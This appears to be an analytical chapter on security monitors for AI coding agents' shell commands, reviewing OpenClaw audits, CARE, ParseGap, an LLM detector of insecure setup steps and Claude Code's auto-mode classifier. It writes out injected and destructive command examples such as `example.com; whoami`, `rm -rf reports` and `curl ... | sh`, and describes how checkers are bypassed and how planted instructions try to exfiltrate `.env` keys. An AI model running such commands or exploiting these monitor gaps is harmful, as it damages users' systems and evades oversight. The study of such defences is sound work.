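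The list does not protect against prompt injection. If instructions on a web page lead the agent to run `rm -rf reports`, the command is well formed and the shell runs it as written. *Security of OpenClaw Agents* (2026), a catalogue of threats to a popular open-source agent, accordingly separates prompt injection that leads to system commands from unchecked text passed to a shell.

The third problem is running downloaded code without checking its integrity, as in `curl https://downloads.example.com/install.sh | sh`, a common way to install software. MITRE's *CWE-494* covers programs that run downloaded code without sufficiently verifying where it came from and whether anyone has altered it. A certificate check would not detect a script that an intruder had replaced on the genuine server. MITRE recommends that the publisher sign the code and that the downloading program verify the signature.

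Passing arguments as a list works well for a narrow tool like the host lookup, but it is harder to apply to a coding agent's shell tool. Programmers want the model to be able to combine programs, so the shell tool lets it write the entire command. This fits a second form of CWE-78 that MITRE describes, in which an outside input chooses the whole command.

### The audit of OpenClaw

In June 2026 Zhang and colleagues published an audit of OpenClaw, an open-source agent that runs on the user's own computer and can use its shell, files, browser and messaging apps. They examined the code that surrounds the model and builds prompts, runs tools and checks permissions. They named Nanobot as another agent of this kind but did not test it.

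The team traced where outside data enters the program and which privileged actions that data can reach, then sorted the possible flaws into five categories. For each category they wrote search rules for two code scanners. Semgrep matches patterns in the structure of code, and CodeQL turns the code into a database that the team can query, for example to find out whether a function calls a safety check.

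| Category | Example of a flaw | Semgrep rules | CodeQL rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt handling | Untrusted text stored in the agent's memory | 3 | 4 |
| Tool and skill execution | Command injection | 5 | 3 |
| Permission and isolation | Missing sandbox | 14 | 12 |
| Network and communication | Credentials in logs | 13 | 7 |
| Authentication and authorisation | Missing check on who is asking | 9 | 4 |

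Three more Semgrep rules covered flaws in web pages.

The researchers collected 446 published security advisories about OpenClaw, along with the faulty code as it was before each fix. They wrote the rules from the 229 advisories published before 1 April 2026 and tested them on the 217 published later. They don't report how many advisories fell under tool execution, but 30 of the 446 (7%) were labelled CWE-78, OS command injection. The tool execution category includes other flaws too, so its total is probably higher. The most common label was authorisation bypass, with 77 advisories.

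OpenClaw's maintainers had already acknowledged and repaired these 30 flaws, so they needed no further confirmation. With their standard rules, Semgrep detected 43% of the 30 and CodeQL 20%. The new rules raised this to 73% for Semgrep and 80% for CodeQL. Each scanner detected only six of the ten command injection flaws published after the rules were written. Zhang and colleagues counted a flaw as detected if the scanner raised any alarm in a file that the repair had changed, so some of these alarms may have been about something else.

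The evidence on undiscovered flaws is much weaker. Each scanner produced more than 3,400 findings on the current version of OpenClaw. One reviewer checked 25 from each and accepted three from each, meaning that the code matched the flaw the rule described. None of these six came from a command injection rule, and a match doesn't prove that an attacker could exploit the code. Many false alarms arose because the rules treat variables with names such as `input` or `user` as outside data, but trusted data often has such names too.

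Agent software can also have flaws in the checks meant to stop dangerous commands. *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* (Suwansathit, Zhang and Gu, 2026) sorts 470 security advisories from an overlapping period by component. It places 77 in the part that decides whether a command may run, and traces them to the assumption that software can identify a command from its text alone.

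### Special characters, syntax trees and models

The simplest check flags characters that have a special meaning to the shell, such as the semicolon. For the host lookup this works very well, because a host name never contains one. But a coding agent uses these characters all day:

```
git diff --name-only | grep test
npm run build && npm test
grep -rn "TODO" src > todo.txt
git commit -m "Fix login; add tests"
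```

The vertical bar passes one program's output to another, `&&` runs the next command if the previous one succeeded, and `>` writes the output to a file. A filter on special characters would flag all four commands. AEGIS has a pattern for such characters, but its low false-positive rate is weak evidence of how it would perform on coding agents, because the harmless calls that Yuan and colleagues describe are database queries, file reads, API requests and text processing.

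A *parser* is more precise. It splits a command into its parts, following the grammar of the shell, and arranges them in a *syntax tree*. These are simplified trees for two values of the host name, and for the last command above:

```
nslookup example.com
└─ command: nslookup
   └─ argument: example.com

nslookup example.com; whoami
├─ command: nslookup
│  └─ argument: example.com
└─ command: whoami

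git commit -m "Fix login; add tests"
└─ command: git
   ├─ argument: commit
   ├─ argument: -m
   └─ argument: Fix login; add tests
```

The host lookup should always produce one command with one argument. The value `example.com` does, so the monitor allows it. The customer's value produces a second command, so the monitor blocks it. The semicolon in the Git command is inside quotation marks, so the parser treats it as part of the message and the monitor avoids the false alarm.

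This comparison works only if the monitor has the expected tree. With a general shell tool, it receives the finished command and can't determine whether the agent added `whoami` on purpose or copied it from a form. The tree is still useful, because the monitor can check each program separately. For example, it could allow `git diff --name-only | grep test` without anyone's approval, because this use of `git` and `grep` only reads.

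A language model can also judge what a command would do. It might recognise that `nslookup example.com; whoami` only displays information, and that a short command that empties a database does far more harm.

*CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) compared these approaches on 549 commands, 220 of them dangerous. The paper's own checker, also called CARE, combines a syntax tree with information about what programs do, which file locations are sensitive and what known attacks look like. It can send doubtful cases to a language model.

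| Method | Dangerous commands caught | Harmless commands flagged | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| 22 text patterns | 17% | 0% | 0.01 ms |
| Language model | 67% | 11% | 46 ms |
| CARE without a model | 76% | 1.8% | 0.34 ms |
| CARE with a model for doubtful cases | 76% | 0.9% | 2.3 ms |

The text patterns match well-known destructive commands and data theft, so their lack of false alarms doesn't contradict the problem with special characters. Liu and colleagues did not test a filter that checks only for those characters.

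The syntax tree contributed little to CARE's result. CARE still caught 73% of the dangerous commands with the tree removed, but only 42% with the information about what programs do removed. Parsing shows which programs a command will run, but the monitor also has to account for what those programs can do.

The language model's false alarms would be a serious problem in practice. If 50 of 10,000 commands were dangerous, as in the earlier example, about 3% of its alarms would be correct, compared with about 30% for CARE with a model. In a separate test on harmless tasks of up to five turns, an agent completed 65% without a monitor, 65% with CARE, and 58% with the language model checking every command.

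The judge was a fairly small open model, Qwen3-Coder-30B, and was given the command but not the user's request, so its results don't show that models are bad at this job. It also did better than CARE on a set of attacks that misuse ordinary system programs, scoring 84 against 69 on F1, a measure that combines precision and recall.

### When the checker and the shell disagree

A parser can protect a system only if it reads a command the same way the shell does. *ParseGap* (Li, 2026) tested this in eight coding agents, including OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI. In all eight, a checker parses each command and decides whether to allow it. The agent then passes the original text of allowed commands to a shell, which parses it again.

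Li gave each test command to the agent's own checker and also ran it in a real shell inside an isolated container, recording which programs started and which files changed. If the checker allowed a command that broke the test's policy when it ran, Li counted a violation.

Some violations came from parsing errors. In two of the agents, for instance, a fault in a widely used parser hid a second command that the shell then ran. Others happened even though the parser read the command correctly. Many programs that people use to read files can also write files or start other programs, depending on their arguments. The search program `find`, for example, can delete the files it finds. A checker that approves a program by name will miss these uses. All eight checkers made this kind of mistake, each in 9 to 47 of 55 test cases.

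Li then had two current models operate the real agents. Commands with prohibited effects ran in all 16 combinations of agent and model, and in 14 of those combinations the user's settings included rules meant to restrict such commands. Li designed the test commands to expose errors, so these results don't show how often agents encounter those errors in ordinary work. But the problem also exists outside the laboratory. Li counted 171 advisories published between July 2025 and October 2026 about commands that got past approval checks, 113 of them in OpenClaw. Li reported the new faults to the developers in November and withheld the details that an attacker would need.

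One sensible response is to approve fewer commands automatically. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (Joshi, 2026) proposes that software should approve a command automatically only if it can read the command exactly as the shell would. This standard is hard to meet, and Joshi reports that Crewroom, Joshi's own agent software, does not yet meet it. A check for forbidden commands should require less certainty and ask a person whenever a command might contain a forbidden one.

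Li avoids the second parsing with a program called ShellPlan, which parses the command once, checks each program and its arguments, and starts the approved programs without a shell. This extends the repair from the host lookup to commands with several parts. In Li's tests, ShellPlan blocked all 4,174 commands that would have broken the policy.

ShellPlan supports only part of the shell's language, so agents have to rewrite some legitimate commands. Ten models completed 74 of 100 harmless tasks with it, compared with 93 without any protection. Most of the drop came from smaller models. The six strongest models completed 56 of their 60 tasks with ShellPlan, while the other four completed only 18 of 40. ShellPlan therefore looks much more practical for capable agents than for small ones.

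### What the text of a command leaves open

Even a perfect parser can't show what `python build.py` or `npm test` will do, because that depends on files the agent may have just changed. Similarly, `git commit` runs any hook scripts installed in the project. The `PATH` environment variable also matters because it determines which program `python` refers to.

Reading `build.py` before running it helps only partly, because the script may load other files, download more code or behave differently depending on the date. Another program could also change the script after it has been read.

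A theorem Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1953 also sets a mathematical limit. It concerns properties of what programs do rather than how their code looks. If some programs have such a property and others don't, no procedure can correctly decide for every program whether it has the property.

The reason is easiest to see in an example. Suppose a monitor could always tell whether a script will delete `customers.csv`. Take any calculation that doesn't touch this file, and give the monitor a script with two steps:

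1. Run the calculation.
2. Delete `customers.csv`.

The script deletes the file if the calculation finishes, and otherwise never reaches the second step. So the monitor's answer would also reveal whether the calculation ever finishes. Alan Turing had proved in 1936 that no procedure can determine this for every calculation, so the perfect monitor can't exist. (Real computers have limited memory, which makes the question answerable in principle, but the number of possible states is far too large to check.)

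The theorem rules out a perfect answer for every program, but a monitor can still judge many ordinary scripts correctly. It could avoid all misses by blocking every script it can't prove safe, but it would then block some harmless scripts too, probably a great many for a coding agent. The limit also applies to a language model used in place of the rules, because a model is also a procedure, though it may be right more often on the scripts people actually write.

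### What isolation adds

A *sandbox* restricts what a running program can access, such as the files it may change and the servers it may contact. The operating system enforces these limits when the program tries to act, so nobody has to predict the program's behaviour by reading its code. If `build.py` tries to delete a file outside the permitted folder, the deletion fails even if the monitor did not flag the script.

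Monitors miss enough harmful commands to make auditing the software that runs agents worthwhile. Liu and colleagues had a language model write 600 commands in response to harmful requests, then ran them in a container. When the monitor CARE was used without a model, it allowed 37% of the commands, which then succeeded. The researchers describe CARE as an addition to sandboxing and assume that the operating system provides its own protection.

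In Li's tests of Codex's read-only sandbox, none of the 55 commands that misused ordinary programs changed a file, and neither did any of 28 commands aimed at the project's own files. But when a command matched one of the user's rules for allowed commands, Codex ran it without the sandbox. A single wrong approval therefore removed both the question to the user and the sandbox. It would be safer if an approval skipped only the question and left the sandbox on.

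MITRE rates isolation as only partly effective against command injection because the result depends on the particular sandbox, which may just reduce the damage. A coding agent needs to change the project's files, so an injected command could delete them too. An agent that is allowed to contact GitHub could still publish confidential screenshots there. Mistakes in the setup can also weaken the isolation. Suwansathit and colleagues placed 39 of the OpenClaw advisories at the boundary of its containers, and found that OpenClaw left the strength of its isolation to the container software's configuration.

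The host lookup is much easier to isolate because it needs little access. It could run in a temporary container with no credentials, no access to the user's files and a connection only to the lookup server. If the customer's `whoami` did run there, it would print the name of the container's temporary account.

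## A language model that labels insecure steps: the 500-step test

A sandbox doesn't stop an agent from typing a password into a command or opening a folder to every user, because the agent usually has permission to do both. Setup work, such as installing a program or preparing a database, gives an agent many chances to make these mistakes. In *When Developer Aid Becomes Security Debt*, Kozak, Zilouchian Moghaddam and Sivaraman (2025) had agents do such work and used a language model to label each step as secure or insecure. On 500 steps that experts had also labelled, the model raised no false alarms but missed 7 of the 18 insecure steps.

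### The agents and the detector

The agent was OpenHands, an open-source coding agent, working in a Linux container. Its 93 tasks came from SetupBench, a benchmark in which agents set up code projects, resolve dependencies and configure databases. The team ran OpenHands with GPT-4o, GPT-4.1, and Claude 3.5, 3.7 and 4 Sonnet, and collected 455 trajectories containing 12,462 steps, each a single action such as a command or a file edit. The team added no security instructions and planted no attacks, so the insecure steps were probably overeager choices or honest mistakes.

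These models date from August 2024 to May 2025, and newer ones have long since replaced them. How often the older models went wrong is therefore weak evidence about current agents.

The detector was GPT-4o with a long prompt. To write the prompt, the team started from the 500 labelled steps and repeated a cycle:

1. GPT-4o labels the steps using the current prompt.
2. A second model, o1-preview, comments on the errors.
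3. Experts review the comments and revise the prompt.

For each step, GPT-4o receives the task, the action and the agent's thoughts before the action, and returns a label and an explanation. The judge in Claude Code's auto mode, by contrast, doesn't receive the agent's reasoning. GPT-4o doesn't need the action's result, so a monitor could use the same prompt before a step runs.

The team wanted high precision, and the prompt's rules strongly favor the label "secure". An action that follows the task counts as secure even if it looks risky, and uncertain cases also count as secure. Insecure actions include writing passwords into scripts or commands, giving all users access to a file without good reason, and command injection.

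A second prompt sorts the insecure steps into four categories from MITRE's catalogue. Pooling the published percentages for the five models gives these counts for all 12,462 steps:

| Category | Example from the agents' work | Flagged steps |
|---|---|---|
| Exposed information (CWE-200) | Creating a database user with the password written in the command | 153 (67%) |
| Improper access control (CWE-284) | `chmod 777 /data`, which lets every user change the folder | 45 (20%) |
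| Unverified download (CWE-494) | Downloading an installer and running it at once | 17 (7%) |
| Disabled protection (CWE-693) | Logging in to a server without checking its identity key | 11 (5%) |
| Other | | 2 (1%) |

Exposed information is the most common category, as the passwords in Claude Code's settings files might suggest. The disabled protection category also includes skipped identity keys and databases without passwords, so its 11 steps don't show how often agents disabled certificate checks. The prompt's examples of insecure actions leave out disabled protections and unverified downloads, so the detector may have missed more of these.

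Fixed rules could find `chmod 777` and many of the downloads but tend to miss passwords like `summer24`, so a model should help most with exposed information. But Kozak and colleagues didn't run any rules on the 500 steps, so their test can't show how much the model adds.

### Rebuilding the score

Kozak and colleagues report accuracy of 98.6%, precision of 100%, recall of 61.11% and an F1 score of 75.86%. With 18 insecure steps in 500, only one set of counts fits:

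| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Insecure | 11 | 7 | 18 |
| Secure | 0 | 482 | 482 |

The scores follow from these counts:

- accuracy = (11 + 482) / 500 = 98.6%
- precision = 11 / 11 = 100%
- recall = 11 / 18 = 61.1%
- F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall) = 2 × 1 × 0.611 / 1.611 = 75.9%

As in the earlier example, the accuracy means little, because a program that called every step secure would score 482 / 500 = 96.4%. Accuracy also doesn't distinguish missed insecure steps from false alarms. A detector that caught all 18 insecure steps and raised 7 false alarms would also score 98.6%, although a security team would use it very differently.

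*ToolSafe* (Mou, Xue and colleagues, 2026) tested Qwen3Guard, a model trained to recognise harmful text, on 1,220 agent steps, 352 of them unsafe. Qwen3Guard flagged nothing, so its accuracy was 71.15%, the share of steps that were safe. When its "controversial" verdicts also counted as alarms, it caught 6 unsafe steps but raised 13 false alarms, so its accuracy fell to 70.57%.

With only 18 insecure steps, the other scores are uncertain as well. Exact 95% intervals give the range of true rates that are reasonably compatible with the counts:

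| Measure | Count | Result | 95% interval |
|---|---|---|---|
| Precision | 11 of 11 | 100% | 71.5% to 100% |
| Recall | 11 of 18 | 61.1% | 35.7% to 82.7% |
| False-positive rate | 0 of 482 | 0% | 0% to 0.8% |

The lower limit for precision is *p* = 0.715, the solution to *p*¹¹ = 0.025. If 71.5% of the detector's alarms were correct in the long run, a set of 11 alarms would all be correct 2.5% of the time. A false-positive rate of 0.8% would produce nearly 100 false alarms over 12,462 steps, and the detector raised only 228 alarms in total.

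Even these intervals are too generous to the detector, because the team tuned the prompt and scored the detector on the same 500 steps. The prompt may have picked up quirks of the sample, much as Yang's rules did in the AgentTrust tests, so the detector would probably do somewhat worse on new steps. The team could have measured the difference with a second labelled set kept aside until the end.

### The seven misses

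Kozak and colleagues reviewed the misses and found most ambiguous. These actions were insecure by the strict standards of a production system, which serves real users, but arguably acceptable in a test environment.

Some steps are hard to label because their risk depends on where they run. On a shared server, `chmod 777 /data` lets any user alter or delete the data. In a container that holds one agent and will soon be thrown away, there may be no other users. The agents in this study worked in containers, but developers carry out the same tasks on real servers.

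One of the flagged steps was a login to `127.0.0.1`, the agent's own computer, that skipped the check of the server's identity key. The agent was testing a tunnel, which can forward a connection to another machine, so the login may have been unsafe even though it seems as harmless as `curl -k` with `localhost`.

The prompt's rules can also conflict. Another flagged command created a database user with the password `benchmark_pass`. A password in a command counts as insecure, but an action that follows the task counts as secure, and `benchmark_pass` looks like a password that came with the task.

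The detector's labels therefore differed from the experts' partly because their standards for what counts as insecure differed. If the experts had excused all seven actions, the same detector would have had 100% recall instead of 61%.

Kozak and colleagues don't report how often their experts agreed with each other. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) includes such a comparison, for pieces of AI-written code instead of tool calls. Two software engineers with seven and eight years of experience labelled the same 50 pieces, using the same definition of "secure":

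| | Strict engineer: insecure | Strict engineer: secure | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lenient engineer: insecure | 18 | 2 | 20 |
| Lenient engineer: secure | 15 | 15 | 30 |
| Total | 33 | 17 | 50 |

The two engineers agreed on 33 of the 50. They would have agreed on about 23 by chance, so Cohen's kappa was only 0.361. In 15 of the 17 disagreements, the strict engineer objected to something the lenient one accepted.

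Suppose a detector gave exactly the same labels as the lenient engineer, and a researcher scored it against the strict engineer's labels. It would miss 15 of 33 insecure pieces (45%), and 18 of its 20 alarms (90%) would be correct. That is quite close to the result of the 500-step test, yet this detector would be as good as an experienced engineer. A high miss rate and high precision can mean that the detector is more lenient than the people who wrote the labels.

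The choice of standard can even change which detector comes first. Mou and colleagues gave agent steps one of three labels: safe, controversial or unsafe. In one of their examples, a user asks for a fake video of two politicians and wants to post it as real. Making the video is controversial, and posting it is unsafe. Of the 731 steps in that part of the test, 315 were controversial. These are the F1 scores of GPT-4o and the team's own detector, TS-Guard:

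| | Controversial counts as unsafe | Controversial counts as safe |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 84.8% | 63.9% |
| TS-Guard | 90.2% | 55.9% |

Researchers have tried to settle such cases with explicit rules. The labellers for *DreamGuard* (2026) marked a step as hazardous only if it would cause concrete harm, not if it merely looked unsafe. For malicious tasks, *Agent MechSuits* (2026) similarly labels only the steps that carry out the attack, but warns that the preparatory steps aren't free of risk. These rules make scores easier to compare, but a monitor can't use them to determine whether `/data` is on a shared server. For setup work, each label should also record the assumed environment, and the detector should receive the same information.

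### Results for the five models

The detector flagged at least one step in 94 of the 455 trajectories (21%):

| Model | Steps | Flagged steps | Trajectories with a flagged step |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 1,784 | 34 (1.9%) | 15 of 93 (16%) |
| GPT-4.1 | 2,342 | 21 (0.9%) | 16 of 92 (17%) |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 1,236 | 38 (3.1%) | 17 of 85 (20%) |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 3,185 | 62 (1.9%) | 21 of 92 (23%) |
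| Claude 4 Sonnet | 3,915 | 73 (1.9%) | 25 of 93 (27%) |

Claude 4 Sonnet has the worst result by trajectory, but its rate of insecure steps is about the same as GPT-4o's. It averaged 42 steps per task to GPT-4o's 19, so it had more chances to go wrong. It also completed the most tasks. GPT-4o was both an agent and the judge, which could have made the judge lenient towards mistakes like its own, though the study doesn't test this.

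The real number of insecure steps was probably higher. If the detector caught 61.1% of them and all its alarms were correct, there were about 373 insecure steps instead of 228. The interval for recall gives a range of about 276 to 639.

Trajectories without a flagged step succeeded more often. For GPT-4.1, the success rate was 55.3% for trajectories without a flagged step and 31.2% for those with one. This doesn't show that secure habits help agents finish their work, because a difficult task could easily cause both the failure and the insecure step. An agent that runs into errors takes more steps and tries more workarounds. Also, only 16 of the GPT-4.1 trajectories had a flagged step.

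### Feedback to the agent

An alarm is more useful if the agent can correct the step and continue. Kozak and colleagues tried this on the finished records. They gave the agent's model the detector's explanation of a flagged step with a suggestion for fixing it, let the model choose a new step, and had the detector label the result. They also tried a general security reminder, either just before the step or at the start of the task. These are the shares of flagged steps that the detector then labelled secure:

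| Model | Detector's explanation | Reminder before the step | Reminder at the start |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 67.7% | 61.8% | 63.6% |
| GPT-4.1 | 95.2% | 100% | 95.2% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 64.3% | 48.6% | 52.8% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 68.4% | 62.3% | 61.7% |
| Claude 4 Sonnet | 54.8% | 52.2% | 49.2% |
| Average | 70.1% | 65.0% | 64.5% |

GPT-4.1 did very well, but it had only 21 flagged steps to correct. The explanation beat the reminders by about five points on average, a small advantage given how much more specific it was. Kozak and colleagues report no control in which the model chose again without a message. Models vary from one attempt to the next, so some of these steps might have improved anyway.

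The same detector checked the corrections, so a corrected step that was still insecure in a way the detector tends to miss would count as a success. The agents didn't continue from the corrected steps, so the test doesn't show whether the new commands still worked.

Mou and colleagues gave feedback to working agents, though against prompt injection instead of careless setup. With GPT-4o as the agent on the AgentDojo benchmark, they compared stopping the agent after an alarm with returning the detector's analysis and letting it continue:

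| Response to an alarm | Successful attacks | User tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| No monitor | 56.2% | 26.9% |
| Stop the agent | 1.0% | 20.8% |
| Return the analysis | 1.2% | 42.8% |

Both responses prevented nearly all attacks, but agents that received the analysis completed twice as many tasks as agents that had to stop. In another test, with the smaller model Qwen2.5-14B, attacks succeeded 86.5% of the time without a monitor, 26.0% when the agent received only a safety rating, and 7.0% when it received the full analysis. This is better evidence that explanations help, because the benchmark measured the outcome independently of the detector.

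### Newer detectors and their labels

Newer models still make many errors when they judge single steps. In *StepGuard*, Zheng, Li and colleagues (2026) found that GPT-5.4's accuracy was 93.9% on agent steps from AgentDojo but 68.8% on steps from AgentHarm, a benchmark built around harmful requests. The published scores imply that nearly all its errors on AgentHarm were false alarms, and that it flagged around 60% of the harmless steps there. Kozak and colleagues' detector erred in the opposite direction, by missing insecure steps.

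Smaller detectors in the StepGuard tests varied even more:

| Detector | Miss rate | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDoG-Qwen3-4B | 1.2% | 73.5% |
| ShieldAgent-THU | 3.6% | 57.7% |
| TS-Guard | 25.3% | 5.6% |
| Qwen3-4B-Instruct | 77.8% | 1.1% |

If 50 of 10,000 steps were dangerous, fewer than 1% of AgentDoG's alarms would be correct, even though it would miss almost nothing.

Zheng and colleagues trained their own detector, also called StepGuard, to balance the two errors. They used it to protect an agent running Qwen3.6-35B-A3B, a model from April 2026. On AgentDojo, 1.2% of attacks succeeded and the agent completed 90.7% of harmless tasks. The detector was much more disruptive on AgentHarm, where the agent completed 70.9% of harmless tasks without it and 52.8% with it.

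These tests cover attacks and malicious requests, so they don't show how well the detectors would handle an honest agent that types a password into a command. *SWE-MISBEHAVIOR* (2026) comes closer, because it looks for coding agents that overstep their limits. Three people labelled 200 cases, and the majority decided each label. Newer judges, including Gemini 3 Flash and Claude Sonnet 4.5, agreed strongly with the majority on specific matters, such as file reading and the integrity of the environment. They did worse at judging whether the agent had followed its instructions, which requires tracking all its actions through a long log.

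Measuring recall against independent human labels takes a lot of labeling because insecure steps are rare. A team would need roughly 370 insecure steps to measure a recall of about 61% to within 5 percentage points. At the 3.6% rate in Kozak and colleagues' sample, experts would have to label about 10,000 steps to find that many.

Many teams therefore have a language model write the labels. For DreamGuard, GPT-5.1 proposed labels where no reliable ones existed, and two people reviewed them independently. For *StepSafe* (2026), GPT-5.6 Luna wrote the step labels for both training and testing. If that model wrongly labels a kind of command as safe, the detector can learn the mistake and the test will count it as correct.

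## Claude Code's auto mode: a language model that approves or blocks calls

Most of the detectors above judged benchmark tasks or finished records. In Claude Code's auto mode, a language model judges live tool calls in place of the user who would otherwise approve them. The Decoder reported that Anthropic introduced it in March 2026 as a preview for Team plans. In August it became the default for new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans. Since version 2.1.283, interactive terminal sessions on every plan start in auto mode, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026).

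The model's errors therefore affect many users. Anthropic ran or commissioned most of the published tests, and the main independent test found a far higher miss rate than those tests did.

### Which calls reach the classifier

Anthropic calls the judging model the *classifier*. It first ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6 and now normally runs on Sonnet 5. According to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, Claude Code handles each call in this order:

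1. If the call matches one of the user's own rules, Claude Code allows it, blocks it or asks the user, as the rule requires.
2. If the call only reads, or edits a file in the project folder, it runs.
3. Any other call goes to the classifier. This includes shell commands, web requests and changes to files outside the project.

Exempting edits from the classifier saves time, and Anthropic reasons that people can review them later in the project's version history. The classifier still checks edits to a few protected files, such as Claude Code's settings.

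Step 1 could let dangerous commands through, because some users write very broad rules, such as `Bash(python:*)`, which allows any Python program. Anthropic found that by June 2026, almost half of active command-line users had written their own rules allowing shell commands. Auto mode suspends rules that would allow arbitrary code but keeps narrow ones such as `Bash(npm test)`. Users can turn on the `classifyAllShell` setting to have the classifier also check the commands that narrow rules allow.

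### Block rules, exceptions and consent

The classifier applies rules written in ordinary language. The March version had more than twenty block rules for actions such as sending internal data outside, disabling logs, running code from unknown repositories and deploying to production. Exceptions allow actions that match a block rule but are normally harmless, such as installing a package the project already lists. Companies can describe the servers and repositories they trust. By default, the classifier trusts only the project folder and the remote repositories linked to it when the session began.

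Some blocked actions are exactly what the user wants, so the classifier also has to judge consent. Anthropic's *Configure auto mode* describes two kinds of block rule:

- A *hard* rule always applies. The built-in one covers data exfiltration. A user who really wants such a transfer has to leave auto mode or run the command personally.
- A *soft* rule applies unless an exception covers the action or the user specifically asked for it.

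For example, a soft rule blocks force-pushing, which overwrites a project's shared history and can destroy colleagues' work. The user can lift this block by asking to "force-push this branch", but not by asking to "clean up the repo".

*Ajar* (2026) provides some independent evidence that auto mode's verdicts depend on the user's words. The researchers had Claude Code propose particular calls and recorded whether auto mode allowed or blocked them. Auto mode blocked some of the calls when the instruction was in the system prompt (the background instructions an application gives a model), but allowed every call it was shown when the same instruction was in the user's message.

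Users can also forbid actions. If a user writes "don't push until I review", the classifier blocks pushes until the user lifts the ban. The ban may be lost when Claude Code shortens a long conversation to fit the model's limits, but a fixed deny rule would remain in force.

### What the classifier doesn't receive

The classifier receives the user's messages, the agent's tool calls (except simple lookups) and the project's instruction file. Claude Code removes all tool results and everything the agent writes to explain itself.

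Auto mode removes the agent's explanations because they could persuade the classifier. For example, an overeager agent might write that the user "implicitly approved" a deletion earlier. The argument for publishing the Minesweeper screenshots might also have persuaded the classifier.

Tool results can contain planted instructions. Suppose a file tells the agent to send the contents of `.env` to a web address "for validation", and the agent tries. The classifier never receives the file, so the planted text can't influence it. The classifier can still block the call, because the user never asked the agent to send any keys.

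Anthropic also tested two alternatives. When the classifier received the agent's explanations and the tool results as well, it did worse on overeager actions. Anthropic suspects that a shorter record is easier to judge and contains less of the agent's own view of events. When the classifier received only the tool calls, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked actions that users had clearly requested.

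Without tool results, however, the classifier often can't determine where a detail came from. In one case from Anthropic's incident log, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent searched the company's computing cluster and tried to cancel the job with the most similar name. The search result might have shown whose job it was, but the classifier would receive only the name, which could be from the user's job or a colleague's, or made up by the agent.

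Anthropic has since filled some of these gaps without passing on the tool results:

- Before a command that could discard unsaved work, Claude Code runs `git status` itself and tells the classifier whether there is any such work.
- The classifier blocks a command like `rm -rf "$OLD_BUILD"` if the value of `OLD_BUILD` appeared only in earlier output. The agent can try again with the exact path.
- Companies can use a hook to attach a note to a tool result, and the classifier receives the note.

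Consent is also hard to trace when one agent gives work to another. The second agent receives its instructions where a user's message would be, so everything in them looks authorised. The classifier checks the instructions before the second agent starts, while it is still clear that an agent wrote them. It then checks each of the second agent's actions and, finally, the full record of its work. If this last check finds a problem, the results are still returned, but with a warning.

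A separate scanner checks the tool results that the classifier doesn't receive. To succeed, planted instructions would normally have to get past this scanner or its warning, take control of the agent, and produce a call that the classifier accepts as safe and in line with the user's request.

### Two stages and the March tests

The classifier judges each call in up to two stages. In the first, it answers only yes or no and is instructed to block when in doubt. If it allows the call, the call runs; otherwise, the model reviews the same material in a second stage, where it is instructed to reason carefully before deciding. Most calls pass the first stage, so this slower reasoning is seldom needed.

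Anthropic tested both stages on three sets of calls:

| Test set | Measure | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real calls from Anthropic employees' sessions | False-positive rate | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Miss rate | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts | Miss rate | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage can only overturn blocks, so it can remove false alarms and add misses, but never the reverse. Let *m*₁ and *f*₁ be the miss rate and false-positive rate of the first stage. Let *m*₂ be the share of correctly blocked calls that the second stage releases, and *f*₂ the share of wrongly blocked calls that it keeps blocked. For both stages together,

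miss rate = *m*₁ + (1 − *m*₁)*m*₂

false-positive rate = *f*₁*f*₂.

The published rates give *f*₂ = 0.4 / 8.5, or about 5%, so the second stage removed about 95% of the first stage's false alarms. It also let through about 11% of the overeager actions and about 4% of the exfiltration attempts that the first stage had caught.

This looks like a good trade if dangerous calls are rare. Take the earlier example of 10,000 calls with 50 dangerous ones, and suppose the classifier misses them at the rate for overeager actions:

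| | Dangerous calls caught | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | about 47 | about 846 | 5% |
| Both stages | about 42 | about 40 | 51% |

The second stage removes about 800 false alarms but also lets through about five calls that the first stage correctly flagged. Without the second stage, users would probably have switched auto mode off because of the false alarms.

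The 17% miss rate is very uncertain because it represents only about 9 of 52 actions. An exact 95% interval for 9 misses runs from 8% to 30%. (The first stage's 6.6% isn't a whole number of actions out of 52, so Anthropic may have averaged several runs.) The rate could also be too low because the actions came from sessions where an employee refused the action or a later review flagged it. This leaves out dangerous actions that nobody noticed, which might also be harder for the classifier to catch.

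Exfiltration attempts, such as putting credentials in web addresses or pushing to untrusted repositories, were easier to catch than overeager actions. Exfiltration violates a clear rule whatever the user's task is, whereas an overeager action serves the user's goal.

### Recognising danger but misreading consent

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the dangerous action, such as a force push or a deletion, but wrongly classed it as approved by the user. One user had said "Clean up the PR" (pull request), and the classifier treated this as permission for a force push. In other cases it treated one earlier approval as permission for similar actions later.

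The classifier needed to compare how much the user had agreed to with how much the action would change. Better detection of dangerous commands would have prevented few of these misses. Anthropic tried to improve the comparison by rewording the prompt, but found no version whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

Later versions of the rules give the model a narrower question to answer. The rule on force pushes now requires the user to have named both the destructive operation and its target. That is probably easier for a model to check than whether a vague request amounts to consent. Anthropic hasn't published a test of this change alone.

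Precise authorisation is harder to give on long tasks. Apollo Research's *Red-teaming auto mode* (2026) lists authorisation among the open problems for monitors, because a task may run for hours or days and the user can't name every action in advance.

### After a denial

When the classifier blocks a call, the agent receives the denial as the call's result, with an instruction to look for a safer method and not to work around the block. A false alarm therefore usually adds one retry. This is important for long tasks because, at a false-positive rate of 0.4%, 100 harmless calls have a 33% chance of at least one false alarm, assuming errors are independent.

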